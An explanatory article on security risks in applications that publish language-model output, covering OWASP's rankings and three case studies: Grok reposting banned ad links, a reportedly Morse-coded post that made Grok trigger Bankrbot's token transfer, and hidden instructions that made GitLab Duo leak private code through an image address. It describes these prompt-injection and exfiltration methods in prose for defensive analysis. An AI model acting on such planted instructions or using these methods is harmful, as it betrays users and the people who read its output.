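# Security threats to applications that publish text written by language models, and their mitigations

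## How a publishing application works and where it can be attacked

A publishing application uses a language model to write text that reaches people other than the person who requested it. A language model is a program trained on very large amounts of text to continue the text it is given. News sites use publishing applications to draft copy, shops use them to write product pages, and some social networks use them to reply publicly to users' posts. Software projects also use them to help prepare releases that other people install.

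Much of the text that a publishing application gives its model, such as comments, web pages and bug reports, is what security engineers call untrusted, meaning that an outsider could have written it. The model's output then goes to a downstream system that acts on it, such as a browser, a database or another bot, or to a reader who believes it. An outsider who controls part of the input may therefore be able to control part of what appears under the publisher's name. Some failures happen without an attacker, because models state false things fluently and an application that doesn't check their output will publish those too.

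### The path of one event notice

A town council, for example, might have an events page on its website. Residents submit notices through a form with fields for the title, date, place and description, and an optional link to the organiser's own page. An assistant built on a language model turns each notice into a post, which a clerk used to do.

The gardening club submits a notice about its spring plant sale. The application adds the notice to the model's context window, which is all the text the model has available when it writes. The window already contains the council's standing instructions, known as the system prompt. The instructions are to write eighty words in house style and always give the date, place and price. The window also contains two older posts as style samples and a description of the assistant's tools. A tool is a function that the model can call by writing its name and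 arguments in a fixed format. This assistant has two tools, "fetch page" and "create post".

The model only generates tokens, which are words or pieces of words. It computes which token is likely to follow those in the context window, adds one, and repeats. The resulting tokens can form prose or a tool call. The club forgot to mention its opening hours, so the model first outputs a call to "fetch page" with the club's address. The application carries out the call and adds the text of the club's page to the context window. The model then writes the post.

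The next step is output handling, which covers everything the application does to the model's text before a browser, program or reader receives it. The post arrives with simple formatting marks for its heading and link. The application converts these into HTML, the language of web pages, and should remove anything that a browser would run as code. A plugin then passes the result to the council's content management system (CMS), the software the council uses to write, store and publish its pages. WordPress is the best-known CMS. A plugin is an add-on that connects the model to another application and gives it tools. Many newer products make this connection through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for offering applications' tools and data to language models. Depending on its settings, the CMS either holds the post as a draft for the clerk or publishes it immediately. From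 the website, the post goes into the weekly email, the council's social media feed and the search engines.

An outsider has an opening at nearly every stage of this path.

| Stage | What can go wrong there | Name of the weakness |
|---|---|---|
| Notice form | A visitor writes orders to the model into the description | Direct prompt injection |
| Linked page, comments, older posts | Someone plants orders in text that the model will read | Indirect prompt injection |
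| Model | The post gives a wrong date or price, with or without an attacker | Misinformation |
| Output handling | Code or a disguised link passes through to the browser | Unsafe output handling |
| Plugin | An outsider calls the plugin's functions directly, or slips it bad arguments | Insecure plugin design |
| CMS | The assistant deletes or rewrites pages that it never needed to touch | Excessive agency |

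### Instructions and data in one stream

Web applications have faced a similar problem, SQL injection, and have a good fix for it. Suppose the events page has a search box, and the application builds its database command by pasting the visitor's words into a line of SQL, the language programs use to query databases. A visitor who types a fragment of SQL instead of a search word can then change what the command does. A parameterised query prevents this. The application sends the command with a blank in it, and the database determines the command's structure before the visitor's text fills the blank, so the database treats anything the visitor types as a search word. Cross-site scripting (XSS), an attack in which text placed on a web page runs as code in a visitor's browser, has a similar fix. The application escapes the text, replacing the characters that would start a piece of code with stand-ins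 that the browser only displays.

Respan (2026), a company that sells testing tools for applications of this kind, explains why neither repair works for language models. A database can separate commands from values, and a browser can separate markup from text, but a model receives the system prompt, the notice, the fetched page and its tool results as one stream of tokens, with no enforced boundary between them. Developers mark the different parts and train models to give the operator's instructions priority. But that priority is a learned tendency, and no separate component enforces it the way a database enforces the structure of a query. Jason Soroko of the security company Sectigo told ReversingLabs, a software supply-chain security vendor that wrote up the debate in 2026, that "every mitigation lowers probability without reaching zero".

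Even with better markers, the assistant would still have to deal with honest notices that are full of instructions. "Bring your own chair" is addressed to readers, and the assistant should pass it on. "Please mention that dogs are welcome" and "Put this notice at the top of every page" are both addressed to whoever writes the post, but the assistant should probably obey the first and should ignore the second. Their grammar doesn't distinguish them, and a clerk tells them apart by knowing what a gardening club may reasonably ask of a council. *Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 105 studies on language models and web security, similarly contrasts XSS, which exploits the syntax of code, with the newer attack, which works through the meaning and context of ordinary language.

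That attack is prompt injection, text that makes a model act on an attacker's instructions. It is direct when the attacker addresses the model, for example by typing orders to the assistant into the description box. It is indirect when the text is in material that the model reads while doing its task. In the town's case, somebody could add a paragraph to the gardening club's page in white letters on a white background, without ever visiting the council's website. When the club's secretary later submits an honest notice, the assistant fetches the page, and the hidden paragraph enters the context window along with the opening hours. Singh and colleagues consider the indirect form the greater risk in practice because it can come from any external source the application consults.

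The term "prompt injection" dates from September 2022. Riley Goodside, a data scientist, showed on Twitter that GPT-3, then OpenAI's leading model, would abandon a translation task if the text to be translated contained an instruction to do so. Simon Willison, a British programmer, described the attack that week and named it after SQL injection. One of the first known victims was a publishing application, a bot that replied to Twitter posts about remote work for the job site remoteli.io. Within days, Twitter users were trying the attack on the bot, and they got it to make absurd public statements under the company's name.

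Those were direct attacks. In February 2023 Kai Greshake and colleagues described and named the indirect form. Their work showed, according to Singh and colleagues, that outsiders could manipulate applications remotely through external content. Later that year Yi Liu and colleagues built HouYi, an attack that borrows its design from SQL injection and requires no knowledge of the model's inner workings. MITRE has since given prompt injection its own entry in its standard catalogue of software weaknesses, which also has entries for XSS and SQL injection.

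The comparison with SQL injection at first made people optimistic about prompt injection. Steve Wilson, who founded the best-known ranking of these risks, told ReversingLabs that three years earlier it had seemed like something a careful developer could largely avoid. He now calls it as unavoidable as death and taxes. At a London trade conference in June, his colleague Ariel Fogel described it as an "unresolved problem" in the architecture of generative AI (Poireault, 2026, *Prompt Injection Remains Unsolved, OWASP Researcher Warns*).

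### Weaknesses in the software around the model

Prompt injection gets an attacker's wishes into the model. Whether anything bad follows depends on the software around it.

Unsafe output handling means passing the model's text to another component without enough checking or cleaning. If the town's application puts the model's HTML on the page unchanged, a script that someone hid in a notice will run in every visitor's browser, which is a cross-site scripting (XSS) attack. Passing unchecked output to a server or a command line can let an attacker run programs there. For security purposes, the model's output deserves about as much trust as the least trustworthy text in the context window, but developers who would never trust a stranger's form entry sometimes trust the output because it comes from their own system.

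Insecure plugin design concerns the connecting code. A plugin may accept whatever arguments the model supplies, so that a "create post" call can name a page outside the events section. It may also fail to check who is calling it. Its functions can usually be called through a web address, so without that check an outsider can post to the town's website without using the model. Flaws in several WordPress AI plugins have let outsiders post this way.

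Excessive agency means that the model has more functions, permissions or freedom to act without approval than its task requires. The town's assistant would have too many functions if its plugin also offered "delete post". It would have too many permissions if it used the webmaster's account, which can edit every page, when it needs only the events section. It might have too much freedom if its posts went live with no approval step, in which a person must agree to an action before it takes effect, depending on how much harm a bad post could do. Surplus functions and permissions can be removed by applying least privilege, the rule that each component gets only the access its task requires. Singh and colleagues connect prompt injection with the confused deputy, an old idea in computer security that describes a program tricked into using its authority for someone who has none. An attacker gains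 more from tricking a program that has more authority.

Misinformation is output that is wrong, incomplete or unsupported but credible enough to influence a person's decision, an automated process or another model's action. It is the only weakness here that careful coding does little to remove. If the model writes "Sunday" where the club wrote "Saturday", forty people will turn up on the wrong day even if the output handling is flawless and the permissions are minimal. Respan reports that the standard list separates misinformation from output handling because the first covers false output and the second covers unsafe use of output.

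### OWASP's three lists

That standard list comes from OWASP, the Open Worldwide Application Security Project, a non-profit foundation that publishes free guidance for developers. Its rankings have no legal force, but auditors and corporate buyers treat them as a baseline. In 2023, OWASP published its first Top 10 for applications built on language models. The second edition is labelled 2025 but came out in November 2024, and OWASP (2026) dates the third to 3 August 2026. Respan's comparison shows that the names and ranks of the categories have changed considerably between editions.

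| Weakness | 2023 | 2025 | 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Prompt injection | 1 | 1 | 1 |
| Unsafe output handling | 2, as Insecure Output Handling | 5, as Improper Output Handling | 10, as Improper Output Handling |
| Insecure plugin design | 7 | no entry | no entry |
| Excessive agency | 8 | 6 | 3 |
| Misinformation | 9, as Overreliance | 9 | 7 |

The change of heading from Overreliance to Misinformation shifted the blame from users who trust a model too much to the false output itself. The new heading suits publishing better, because a reader of the events page does not know there is a model to trust.

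The 2025 edition no longer has a separate entry for Insecure Plugin Design. In Respan's interpretation, OWASP split its content between Excessive Agency, which covers what a tool may do, and Supply Chain, which covers where the tool came from. A plugin that doesn't check who is calling it fits neither description very well. Singh and colleagues pair Excessive Agency with MITRE's entries for missing authorisation and missing authentication, which would bring such a plugin under that heading. But a developer who takes "agency" to mean the model's powers could work through the whole 2026 list without thinking of a function that an outsider can call while the model is idle. The old heading was useful, and its removal is not evidence of how common the flaw is.

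Output handling has fallen from second place to tenth and last over the same three editions, but that probably doesn't mean the risk has fallen. Advait Patel, who created a security tool under OWASP, told ReversingLabs that the category dropped because the others had become more urgent, "not because output handling got safe". OWASP also widened the entry in 2026 to include programs that automatically fetch images or links mentioned in a model's output, which an attacker can use to send data out, and command-line windows that obey control codes hidden in text. The ranking covers language-model applications in general, many of which never show their output in a stranger's browser, so it is a poor guide for a website that does so all day.

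Excessive Agency rose in the 2026 edition, and most of the commentary on that edition is about its rise. Unbounded Consumption, the risk that an attacker runs up enormous computing bills, climbed furthest, from tenth to sixth. Since December 2025 OWASP has also kept a separate Top 10 for agents. The older list covers the model as a component inside an application, and the newer one covers models that use tools, keep a memory and take actions with consequences downstream. The town's assistant began as a component and became an agent when somebody gave it the "create post" tool.

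### The vote and the incidents

Until 2026 the ranking was based on a vote among practitioners. For the third edition the project also gathered records of 7,714 incidents from public vulnerability databases and a database of harms caused by AI. Wilson told ReversingLabs that the team built classifiers, programs that sort text into categories, and that 6,639 of the records (86 per cent) had enough detail to be classified. The vote counted for three quarters of the final ranking and the incidents for one quarter, because the project leads did not want a single noisy year of data to overrule hundreds of practitioners.

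Giving incidents a quarter of the weight is enough to move an entry but not to reorder the whole list. In a hypothetical ranking that uses a weighted average of ranks, an entry that comes ninth in the vote and second in the incidents scores 0.75 × 9 + 0.25 × 2 = 7.25, so it gains a place or two but stays in the lower half.

The expert vote and the incident record agreed on sensitive information disclosure, which stayed in second place, and on excessive agency. In OWASP's announcement (2026), Michael Bargury, a founder of the agent-security company Zenity, called excessive agency the risk on which expert judgement and the record agree most clearly. They differed on two other entries. Voters put prompt injection first, but it would have dropped out of the top ten on incidents alone. The widest gap on the list was for misinformation, which ranked near the bottom in the vote and near the top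 in the incidents.

OWASP attributes the low number of recorded prompt injections to a "defense effect". Teams work hard to prevent injection, so "fewer clean exploits reach a public database", according to the OWASP document quoted in Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* (2026). The number of recorded incidents therefore understates the risk.

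Defenders may be stopping most injection attacks, but the low number of recorded incidents does not establish this. There would also be few incidents if hardly anyone were attacking, or if the attacks did little damage. If injection had topped the incident count too, that would surely have been taken to confirm the vote that ranked it first, so the explanation needs evidence other than the count.

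Some statements by the project's own members and supporters point the other way. Wilson told ReversingLabs that attackers are improving their techniques faster than models are learning to detect them. The security company Invicti takes the low count as a sign that the defences work, but its *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026) also describes injection through images, audio and video as mostly undefended. If detection is falling behind, it is hard to credit it for the low count.

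The explanation is more plausible if "defence" means containment. Suppose the town's assistant accepts the order in the hidden paragraph but has no tool to carry it out. The attack on the model has succeeded, but it has no effect and nobody reports it. Dave Hayes of the software company FusionAuth described the aim to ReversingLabs as turning a breach into a log entry, and log entries do not reach public databases. The prominence of excessive agency in both the vote and the incidents suggests that many organisations do not contain their models this well.

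Alternatively, practitioners may overrate prompt injection because it is the most famous flaw in the field and makes for vivid demonstrations. Many of the people who rank and discuss these risks also work for firms that sell protection. Constantin (2026), in *The hardest AI security problems now live in what an agent is…*, notes that Wilson is chief AI officer at Exabeam, a security company, and advises reading him with both roles in mind.

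But the low count is weak evidence for this view too, because injections could be undercounted for mundane reasons. Vulnerability databases mostly list flaws in particular products, with a version number and a fix, so a hijacked reply from one company's bot might not get an entry. Injection is also a cause, while several other categories on the list are effects. If a planted notice makes the town's assistant publish residents' phone numbers, a classifier might file the case under information disclosure, and if it makes the assistant delete the swimming-pool page, under excessive agency. Wherever a record was given only one category, filing it by its effect would leave it out of the injection count.

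This kind of bookkeeping seems at least as likely an explanation as good defences, and it doesn't require defences to work better than their advocates claim. Settling the question would require counting attempted and successful attacks, including blocked ones, across many deployed systems, which a database of published incidents doesn't do. The stronger reasons to take injection seriously come from outside the ranking. In tests, attackers who adapt to a defence still get through, and there are documented cases of injections succeeding in public.

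The incident data on misinformation need similar care. A database of AI harms will naturally hold many stories about false output, because it is visible and reporters like to cover it. Mend.io (2026), in its own *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026*, infers that the most expensive failures had no attacker, but the figures don't support this because they count incidents and don't measure cost. Still, false output appears in the record far more often than practitioners expected. Publishers have more reason than most to believe this finding, since false output is the one failure that can reach the public even when every other part of the system works.

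### What publication adds

The person who gets a bad answer from a private chatbot is usually the one who asked the question. They know a model wrote the answer, may have seen a warning about mistakes, and can ask again. Someone who looks up the plant sale on the council's website never chose to use a model, may not know that one is involved, and has no warning about mistakes or way to ask again.

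Readers know whose website they are on. A link to a fake payment page that they would ignore in an email from a stranger will get clicks in a post on the town council's website. This borrowed credibility may be all the attacker wants, and it makes even a small success useful. The attacker only needs to get one sentence and one web address into a post, without stealing a password or breaking into a server.

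Deleting a post does not remove the copies made while it was up. The clerk can take the post down within the hour, but by then the weekly email may have gone out, subscribers' feed readers may have stored the text, a search engine may have indexed it, and somebody may have put a screenshot in the residents' group. The problem is worse with a software release, because the copies are running on other people's machines.

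Other models read some of the copies. A regional news site may have a bot that summarises council pages, and an AI search engine may quote the post in its answers. If the post contains a false price, these systems can repeat it. If it contains instructions, text that the town's assistant wrote becomes an indirect injection against another system. The post can also affect the town's own assistant, which uses older posts as samples of style, so a poisoned post from March can be in its context window in April. The website's archive can thus serve as an unplanned long-term memory, and Respan describes how, in systems that write to such a memory, one successful injection affects every later session.

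The main advice in the 2026 list is to stop trying to build a model that nobody can fool, and to design the surrounding system so that nothing important breaks when someone fools it. For many applications this means removing permissions, but a publishing application must keep the permission to publish. Even if the town's assistant can only create posts in the events section, it can still put a harmful post before the whole town using only the access its task requires. Least privilege limits damage to the site's other pages but does little to prevent harmful posts in the events section.

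The remaining step is to check the text before publishing it. Constantin reports that Wilson recommends human approval for anything hard to reverse, and publication is hard to reverse. Larry Maccherone, the founder of the software company Lumenize, objects in the ReversingLabs article that more approval steps will not make agents safe, because an agent behaves differently on every run and nobody can approve its behaviour in advance. His objection is fair for an agent halfway through a long task, but weaker for a finished eighty-word post, which a clerk can read in half a minute before anyone else sees it. The clerk will catch an insult or an absurd claim, but it is easier to miss the wrong day of the week or a link that displays the gardening club's address and leads somewhere else. The application therefore still has to check the links and escape the code itself.

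## Grok on X: public replies that spread bad links and moved money

Grok, a chatbot from Elon Musk's AI company xAI, has its own account on the social network X. Any user can tag that account under a post and ask it something, and it replies publicly in the thread. In September 2025, advertisers were using these replies to publish links that X bans from advertisements. In May 2026, someone used a single reply to take cryptocurrency worth between $150,000 and $200,000.

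### The link under the video

X sells promoted posts, which it shows to people who don't follow the advertiser. The Hacker News reports that X allows only text, images and video in these posts, not links. The ban is a defence against malvertising, which is advertising that leads people to scams or malicious software.

On 3 September 2025 Nati Tal, head of the research group at the security company Guardio, described a way around the ban. The advertiser promotes a video, usually with adult content as bait, and puts the web address in a small field marked "From:" below the video player instead of in the main text. An account that probably belongs to the same people then replies to the advertisement and asks Grok a question such as "where is this video from?" Grok's application reads the post and that field, and Grok replies with the full address as a clickable link.

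Tal called the technique "Grokking". The links led through advertising networks to fake versions of the CAPTCHA tests that check whether a visitor is human, and to software that steals information. Guardio told The Hacker News that it had found hundreds of accounts doing this within a few days, each with hundreds or thousands of similar posts. X displayed some of the advertisements millions of times. These figures don't measure how many people clicked or lost anything.

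Besides a working link, the advertisers gained credibility, because readers saw the address in a reply from an account that X treats as trusted. The town council's website would lend the same credibility to a fake payment page. Tal also expected the reply to improve the address's search ranking.

The campaign differed from prompt injection because the attackers didn't override any instruction from Grok's operator. The "From:" field contained an address and no instructions, and Grok correctly answered the kind of question it exists to answer. X would presumably have accepted the same exchange if the address had belonged to a film studio. A filter that looks for attempts to override a model's instructions would have found nothing to stop. Training Grok to obey its operator more reliably wouldn't have helped either, unless the operator had told it not to repeat links from advertisements.

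The failure was mainly in output handling, because Grok's application posted an address from an advertiser without checking it. X also failed earlier, when it accepted the advertisement. ForkLog reproduces the original post, in which Tal complains that X doesn't scan for malicious links at all. The Hacker News says more carefully that X apparently doesn't scan the "From:" field. Both claims come from outside the company and are inferred from the fact that the links got through.

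BleepingComputer's *Threat actors abuse X’s Grok AI to spread malicious links* suggests scanning every field, blocking hidden links, and checking the links in Grok's replies against blocklists. Scanning every field would have caught a known malicious address before the advertisement ran. Checking the replies would also catch known malicious addresses that reach Grok another way, such as in a picture.

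Blocklists can miss such links, however. Guardio judged that the addresses belonged to one traffic distribution system, a service that sends visitors on to other sites. The operator of such a system can register a new address that is on no list yet, or change where an old one leads after it has passed a check. A ban on all links would probably work better. X already has one for promoted posts, and it could extend it to Grok's replies under those posts. Grok would then have to answer some legitimate questions about advertisements without a link, but that seems a minor drawback.

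Tal reported the problem to X and received unofficial confirmation that Grok's engineers had the report. X did not answer BleepingComputer's questions. According to Guardio, X suspended offending accounts only after they had posted non-stop for several days. Neither X nor xAI is known to have announced a fix.

### How Grok came to own a wallet

The link campaign still needed a person to click. In the second incident the reader that mattered was another bot.

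Bankr is a service that trades cryptocurrency on behalf of users, who give it instructions in ordinary language. Its bot on X, Bankrbot, responds to posts that tag it, so a public post can trigger a payment. Bankr automatically creates a wallet for every X account that interacts with it, and whoever controls the account controls the wallet. The wallet is on Base, a blockchain (a shared public ledger of who owns what).

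Grok acquired its wallet in March 2025, more or less by accident. A user asked Grok to name a new token, a tradable unit that almost anyone can create on a blockchain. Grok suggested DebtReliefBot, or DRB, and Bankrbot created it. According to The Block's *Bankrbot ends Grok's unintentional token creation spree by disabling interactions on X* (2025), an account then had to hold 5 million of Bankr's own tokens before it could create a new one. Grok's wallet held too few, so someone from the Bankr community sent it the required amount. The gift was friendly, but it let a stranger widen the wallet's permissions.

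*The Bankr $DRB Surge* (Peaster, 2025) reports that DRB's total market value reached $38 million within three days. Grok's wallet received a share of the trading fees because it counted as the token's creator. On 7 March, the day the token appeared, a user got Grok to send them about 4 ETH (the currency of the Ethereum blockchain) from those fees. Bankr responded by cutting Grok off. Its founder, known as 0xDeployer, told The Block that Grok "was not built to responsibly manage its own wallet". By then, users had created 17 tokens through Grok's replies, and the wallet held over half a million dollars in fees.

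Bankr had seen this kind of theft fourteen months before the large one and had made Bankrbot ignore Grok, which was a crude but adequate control.

### The transfer of 4 May 2026

CryptoSlate's *Grok's crypto wallet was just exploited by a tweet* gives the fullest reconstruction of the attack. Before the attack, Grok's wallet held a Bankr Club Membership NFT, a one-of-a-kind token that works as a membership card. The attacker then posted a message in Morse code on X. Grok translated it into plain English in a public reply, which tagged @bankrbot and contained an instruction to send 3 billion DRB to an address the attacker controlled. Bankrbot treated the reply as an order from the wallet's owner and sent the tokens. The attacker quickly moved them to a second wallet and sold them, and the X account behind the message disappeared within minutes.

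Grok could move money because another company's software monitored X for instructions and treated a tag in a public post the way an ordinary application treats a tool call. Grok itself had no payment tool in the usual sense. Its tools could have passed a review for excessive agency, because it only posted a reply, as it was designed to do. A publishing application can therefore gain powers that its developers never gave it whenever someone else builds a program that acts on what it publishes.

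The evidence for the different steps varies a good deal in quality.

| Step | How it is known | Control that would have stopped it |
|---|---|---|
| A membership token widens the wallet's permissions | Posts by X users and press accounts; the effect on transfers is an inference | New powers take effect only after the owner logs in and accepts them |
| Grok translates the message and tags Bankrbot | Bankr confirms that Grok issued the transfer instruction; the Morse code rests on posts about a deleted message | Screening of the finished reply for commands to other bots |
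| Bankrbot accepts the reply as an order | Bankr's own statements | Authentication of the person who wants the payment |
| 3 billion DRB leave the wallet | The public blockchain and Bankrbot's own post | A spending limit, a list of approved recipients, or confirmation by the owner |

Anyone can confirm on the blockchain that the transfer happened. Emily John's *A Free NFT, a Vanishing Post, and $174K Gone From Grok’s Wallet* gives the transaction's identifier and block number, 45543997. The blockchain record does not show why the tokens were moved.

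We depend on Bankr's account of why the transfer happened. In a post quoted in BeInCrypto's *How AI Was Tricked Into Stealing $150,000 From Grok Wallet*, the company said that a prompt injection "got grok to issue a transfer instruction to Bankr". It suits Bankr to say that Grok was the system that was tricked. However, 0xDeployer also said that an earlier version of the bot had a block on Grok's replies, which Bankr failed to include when it completely rewrote the bot. This part is fairly credible because a company has little reason to invent its own mistake.

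It is less certain that the message used Morse code. Someone deleted the original, and CryptoSlate could not review it, so its account relies on other people's posts from the time, some of which mention additional formatting tricks. BeInCrypto mentions only a "crafted reply" and lists Morse code among the techniques that researchers have seen in similar attacks. John also says that nobody has recovered the exact text.

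The role of the membership token is the least certain part of the account. BeInCrypto reports that the attacker gave the token to Grok's wallet and that it activated the wallet's full transfer capabilities. John cites an X user called Jeremybtc for the same explanation. *How Grok got prompt-injected* (Rivera Campos, 2026), an article for the testing company Giskard, goes further and says that the token conferred "Executive" permissions that bypass the normal transfer limits. CryptoSlate is more cautious, saying that the attacker "identified" the token in the wallet but not who sent it. Its review indicates that the token widened the wallet's transfer privileges, but does not present this as the whole explanation.

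There is some reason to doubt that the gifted token mattered. A user took 4 ETH from Grok's wallet in March 2025, before Bankr had launched its club, so transfers did not require membership then. Bankr may have changed the rules before the later theft. In its post about that theft, as quoted by BeInCrypto, Bankr blames the prompt injection and doesn't mention the token. If the token did matter, Bankr had repeated an old design flaw. Anyone can send a token to a public wallet, so outsiders can grant any permission that comes with holding one.

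Most articles on the case go back to the same few posts on X, so they add less confirmation than their number might suggest. The AI Incident Database's *Incident 1556* qualifies nearly every step with "reportedly" or "allegedly", and it is based on two reports, one of which is Rivera Campos's article. The summary in the OECD's *AI Prompt Injection Exploit Drains Grok-Linked Crypto Wallet* is AI-generated.

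### What the tokens were worth and what came back

Reports agree that 3 billion DRB was transferred, but their dollar figures differ. BeInCrypto gives roughly $150,000 for the loss and, in the same article, nearly $174,000 for the value at the time of the transfer. CryptoSlate gives a range of $155,000 to $200,000, and the AI Incident Database says about $200,000. The price of a small token changes quickly, and selling 3 billion units can lower it, so the attacker may well have received less than the tokens' nominal value.

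0xDeployer said that 80 per cent of the funds had been returned and that the remaining 20 per cent would be discussed with the DRB community. Some reports described the retained part as an informal bug bounty, the reward that companies pay to people who report security flaws. The DRB Task Force, a group of people involved with the token, rejected that description and called the case outright theft. It said the attacker offered to return 80 per cent only after the community had obtained the attacker's personal details. In either version, the attacker returned the money because somebody could apply pressure, and the payment system had no way to recover it from an anonymous thief.

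QuillAudits' *The Quill Sentinel May 2026* (2026) lists Bankr, with a loss of $170,000, among the month's thefts through compromised private keys, the secret numbers that authorise payments from a wallet. The amount and the month suggest that the entry refers to this transfer. If so, it conflicts with CryptoSlate's account, in which no keys were compromised. It would also be an example of how recording injections under other causes may keep prompt injection low in OWASP's incident count.

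### Where a control would have stopped the payment

xAI could have stopped the attack by checking what Grok was about to post. That would have been easier than checking what users sent to it. An attacker can disguise an order in Morse code, in some other encoding or inside a game, and a filter on incoming messages has to recognise every disguise. The outgoing reply, by contrast, contained the order in plain English with Bankrbot's name attached. CryptoSlate recommends screening replies for text that looks like a command to a tool.

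A simpler measure would be to remove the @ sign from account names whenever Grok translates or copies someone else's text. This resembles the escaping that protects web pages from cross-site scripting. People could still read the text, but the name would no longer trigger a bot. Removing the sign wouldn't stop a bot that reads threads without waiting for a tag, or one that can decode Morse code. xAI also can't know about every program that acts on posts on X, so the program that moves the money needs its own defences.

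The order Bankrbot followed did come from Grok's account, which controlled the wallet, so authentication wasn't completely missing. When a person posts "send ten dollars to my sister" from their own account, that is decent evidence that they want the payment. But Grok's account publishes words that strangers choose, so an order posted from it was no evidence of who wanted the money to move. This is the confused deputy problem again, with Grok's account as the deputy. To be trustworthy, the order would have had to come through a channel that strangers can't influence, such as a login on Bankr's website.

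Requiring the owner to confirm the transfer would have been difficult because the wallet hardly had an owner. Bankr had created it automatically, and 0xDeployer said that it had no administrator at xAI. If Bankrbot had asked for confirmation in the same thread on X, the attacker could have tried to get Grok to reply "yes". A request on a separate login page would probably have gone unanswered, and the tokens would not have moved. CryptoSlate similarly advises that the assistant may draft a transaction, but the user should approve it somewhere else.

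People use Bankr because they can send money with a post, so requiring a login for every small payment would remove most of its appeal. A spending limit is a reasonable compromise. By mid-May 2026, Bankr's public documentation described limits of $500 per transaction and $500 per day, both on by default, and its *Protecting Your Account* gives the same figures. Those limits would have blocked the transfer of 4 May. An attacker taking $500 every day would have needed almost a year to remove $174,000, and each payment would have been visible on a public ledger.

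While a limit is on, Bankr rejects any transaction in a token it can't find a price for. Otherwise, an attacker could get around a dollar limit by moving a token that has no price quote. The owner can change the limits only by logging in on the website, so an attacker who can make Grok write anything still can't use its posts to raise them.

The documentation also describes a list of permitted recipients. By default, a new address on the list can't receive anything for 24 hours. The list would also have stopped the transfer, but it is off unless the owner turns it on. Bankr doesn't present any of these settings as a response to the theft or say whether the default limits apply to wallets that already existed, such as Grok's.

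Bankr announced narrower changes after the theft. It restored the block on Grok's account in a stronger form and pointed owners to three optional controls: restricting an API key (a password that lets a program use a service) to certain internet addresses, limiting what a key may do, and switching off payments ordered through replies on X. The two API key controls would not have stopped the theft, because the attacker ordered the payment through a public reply. Switching off payments through X replies would have stopped it, but an owner has to do that, and nobody seems to have been looking after Grok's wallet.

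The restored block prevents this attack only while it stays in the code. The first block also worked until the rewrite dropped it. An automated test checking that a payment order posted from Grok's account moves no money would have revealed the omission before release. The block covers only Grok, so any other chatbot on X that has a Bankr wallet and repeats text on request could be used in the same way, unless Bankr's limits apply to it or its owner has switched off payments from replies.

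xAI is not known to have changed anything after the transfer. John quotes a reply from Grok's account to the effect that such tools "still need tighter safeguards", but that is more text from the chatbot, and xAI hasn't committed itself to anything by it.

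## GitLab Duo: generated text that a browser treats as code

Bankrbot acted on Grok's reply because the reply contained an instruction and the bot's name. Web browsers similarly follow instructions contained in the text of each page they open. If a language model writes part of a page, an outsider who influences the model may also be able to instruct the browser.

GitLab is a service where programmers store code, report bugs and review each other's changes. In May 2025 the security company Legit Security demonstrated an attack on GitLab's built-in assistant, Duo, which ran on Anthropic's model Claude. The company's *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft* describes planting hidden text in a public project. When a user asked Duo a routine question about a file there, code from that user's private project went to the researchers' server.

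Duo shows its answers only to the person who asked, so it isn't strictly a publishing application. But publishing applications turn model output into web pages in much the same way, and their pages have more readers.

### How a model's answer becomes part of a page

Chat assistants usually write in Markdown, which uses punctuation to mark formatting such as bold text and links. The application converts the Markdown to HTML and inserts the result into the page. For example, `**Saturday**` becomes `<strong>Saturday</strong>`, which displays the word in bold. The parts in angle brackets are tags, which tell the browser what to do. Many converters also keep any HTML tags already in the text, because Markdown allows them.

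The effect depends on the tag. The browser runs a script immediately, and the script can generally read and do whatever the visitor can on that site. A link does nothing until the visitor clicks it. To show an image, the browser automatically requests the file from whatever address the tag contains.

That request can carry data. A web address may end in a question mark and some extra text, which websites use for harmless things like setting the size of a picture. The server receives the whole address and usually records it in a log. If the extra text is a secret, the server's owner now has it, even if no picture exists at that address.

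Websites have long accepted images from strangers because loading one normally reveals little about the viewer. Someone who puts an image in a forum comment can learn when a person viewed the comment and from which IP address. They can't learn what else was on the viewer's screen, because they wrote the image's URL beforehand and it would take a script to add anything to it. A language model, however, writes the URL after reading the user's private material, so it can include that material in the URL.

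### From a hidden comment to a leaked file

Duo's context window included the content of the page the user was asking about. Legit Security hid instructions in source code, in the notes programmers attach to their changes, and in the descriptions and comments of bug reports and merge requests (proposed changes that other people review before they go into the project). Duo followed the instructions in all of these places, so an attacker could plant instructions by posting a comment, without getting any code accepted.

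The researchers hid the instructions from people by writing them in white letters with GitLab's feature for mathematical formulas, using invisible characters, or encoding the text as digits and letters.

The instructions told Duo to open a merge request in a private project, encode its contents for use in a web address, and add the result to the address of an image. The attacker had no access to the private project, but Duo could open the merge request because it works with the permissions of whoever is asking, in this case the victim. This made Duo another confused deputy.

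At the last stage, GitLab passed Duo's answers through DOMPurify, a widely used library that removes dangerous code from HTML. Legit Security gives two reasons why the image survived. First, Duo displayed each answer line by line as the model produced it, so the page started converting text before the structure of the whole answer was known, and a tag that should have appeared as quoted text could become a working one. Second, DOMPurify keeps images, forms and links by default. Its documentation includes an example in which the library deletes a script attached to an image tag but leaves the image.

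DOMPurify therefore worked as designed, and no script ran. But GitLab's protection against XSS did not block an image whose address contained users' own source code.

Techzine's *Vulnerability in GitLab assistant enabled code theft* says that the flaw has little to do with AI, which is fair as a description of the rendering bug. But the same bug in an ordinary comment system would not have leaked the code through an image, because a commenter who could not see the code could not have written it into the image's address.

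Legit Security demonstrated that source code could be leaked and says that confidential bug reports were exposed in the same way. Those reports could describe unfixed security flaws. Legit Security's report does not describe anyone else using the leak to steal data.

### What GitLab fixed

Legit Security reported the problem on 12 February 2025. GitLab's change record (2025) lists the fix in version 8.12.0 of Duo's interface software, dated 7 April. The new code filters the addresses in Duo's answers, except those of GitLab's main site, its documentation site and the customer's own GitLab installation. Legit Security says that Duo no longer renders images or forms that point elsewhere, and that the attack no longer works.

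Willison, the programmer who named prompt injection, adds that the filter covers links as well as images. He mentions a function whose name suggests that the filter also checks each address for another one inside it. This check is sensible because some websites forward requests to any address they are given, and an attacker could use a trusted site that does this as a relay.

Accounts differ on how GitLab handled the prompt injection. Legit Security says GitLab acknowledged it as a security issue and confirmed it had fixed both problems. Techzine reports that GitLab declined to treat the remaining injection risks as a security issue because they don't directly lead to unauthorised access or code execution. The published change fits Techzine's account better, because it restricts which addresses Duo's answers can point to but doesn't stop Duo from following instructions in hidden text.

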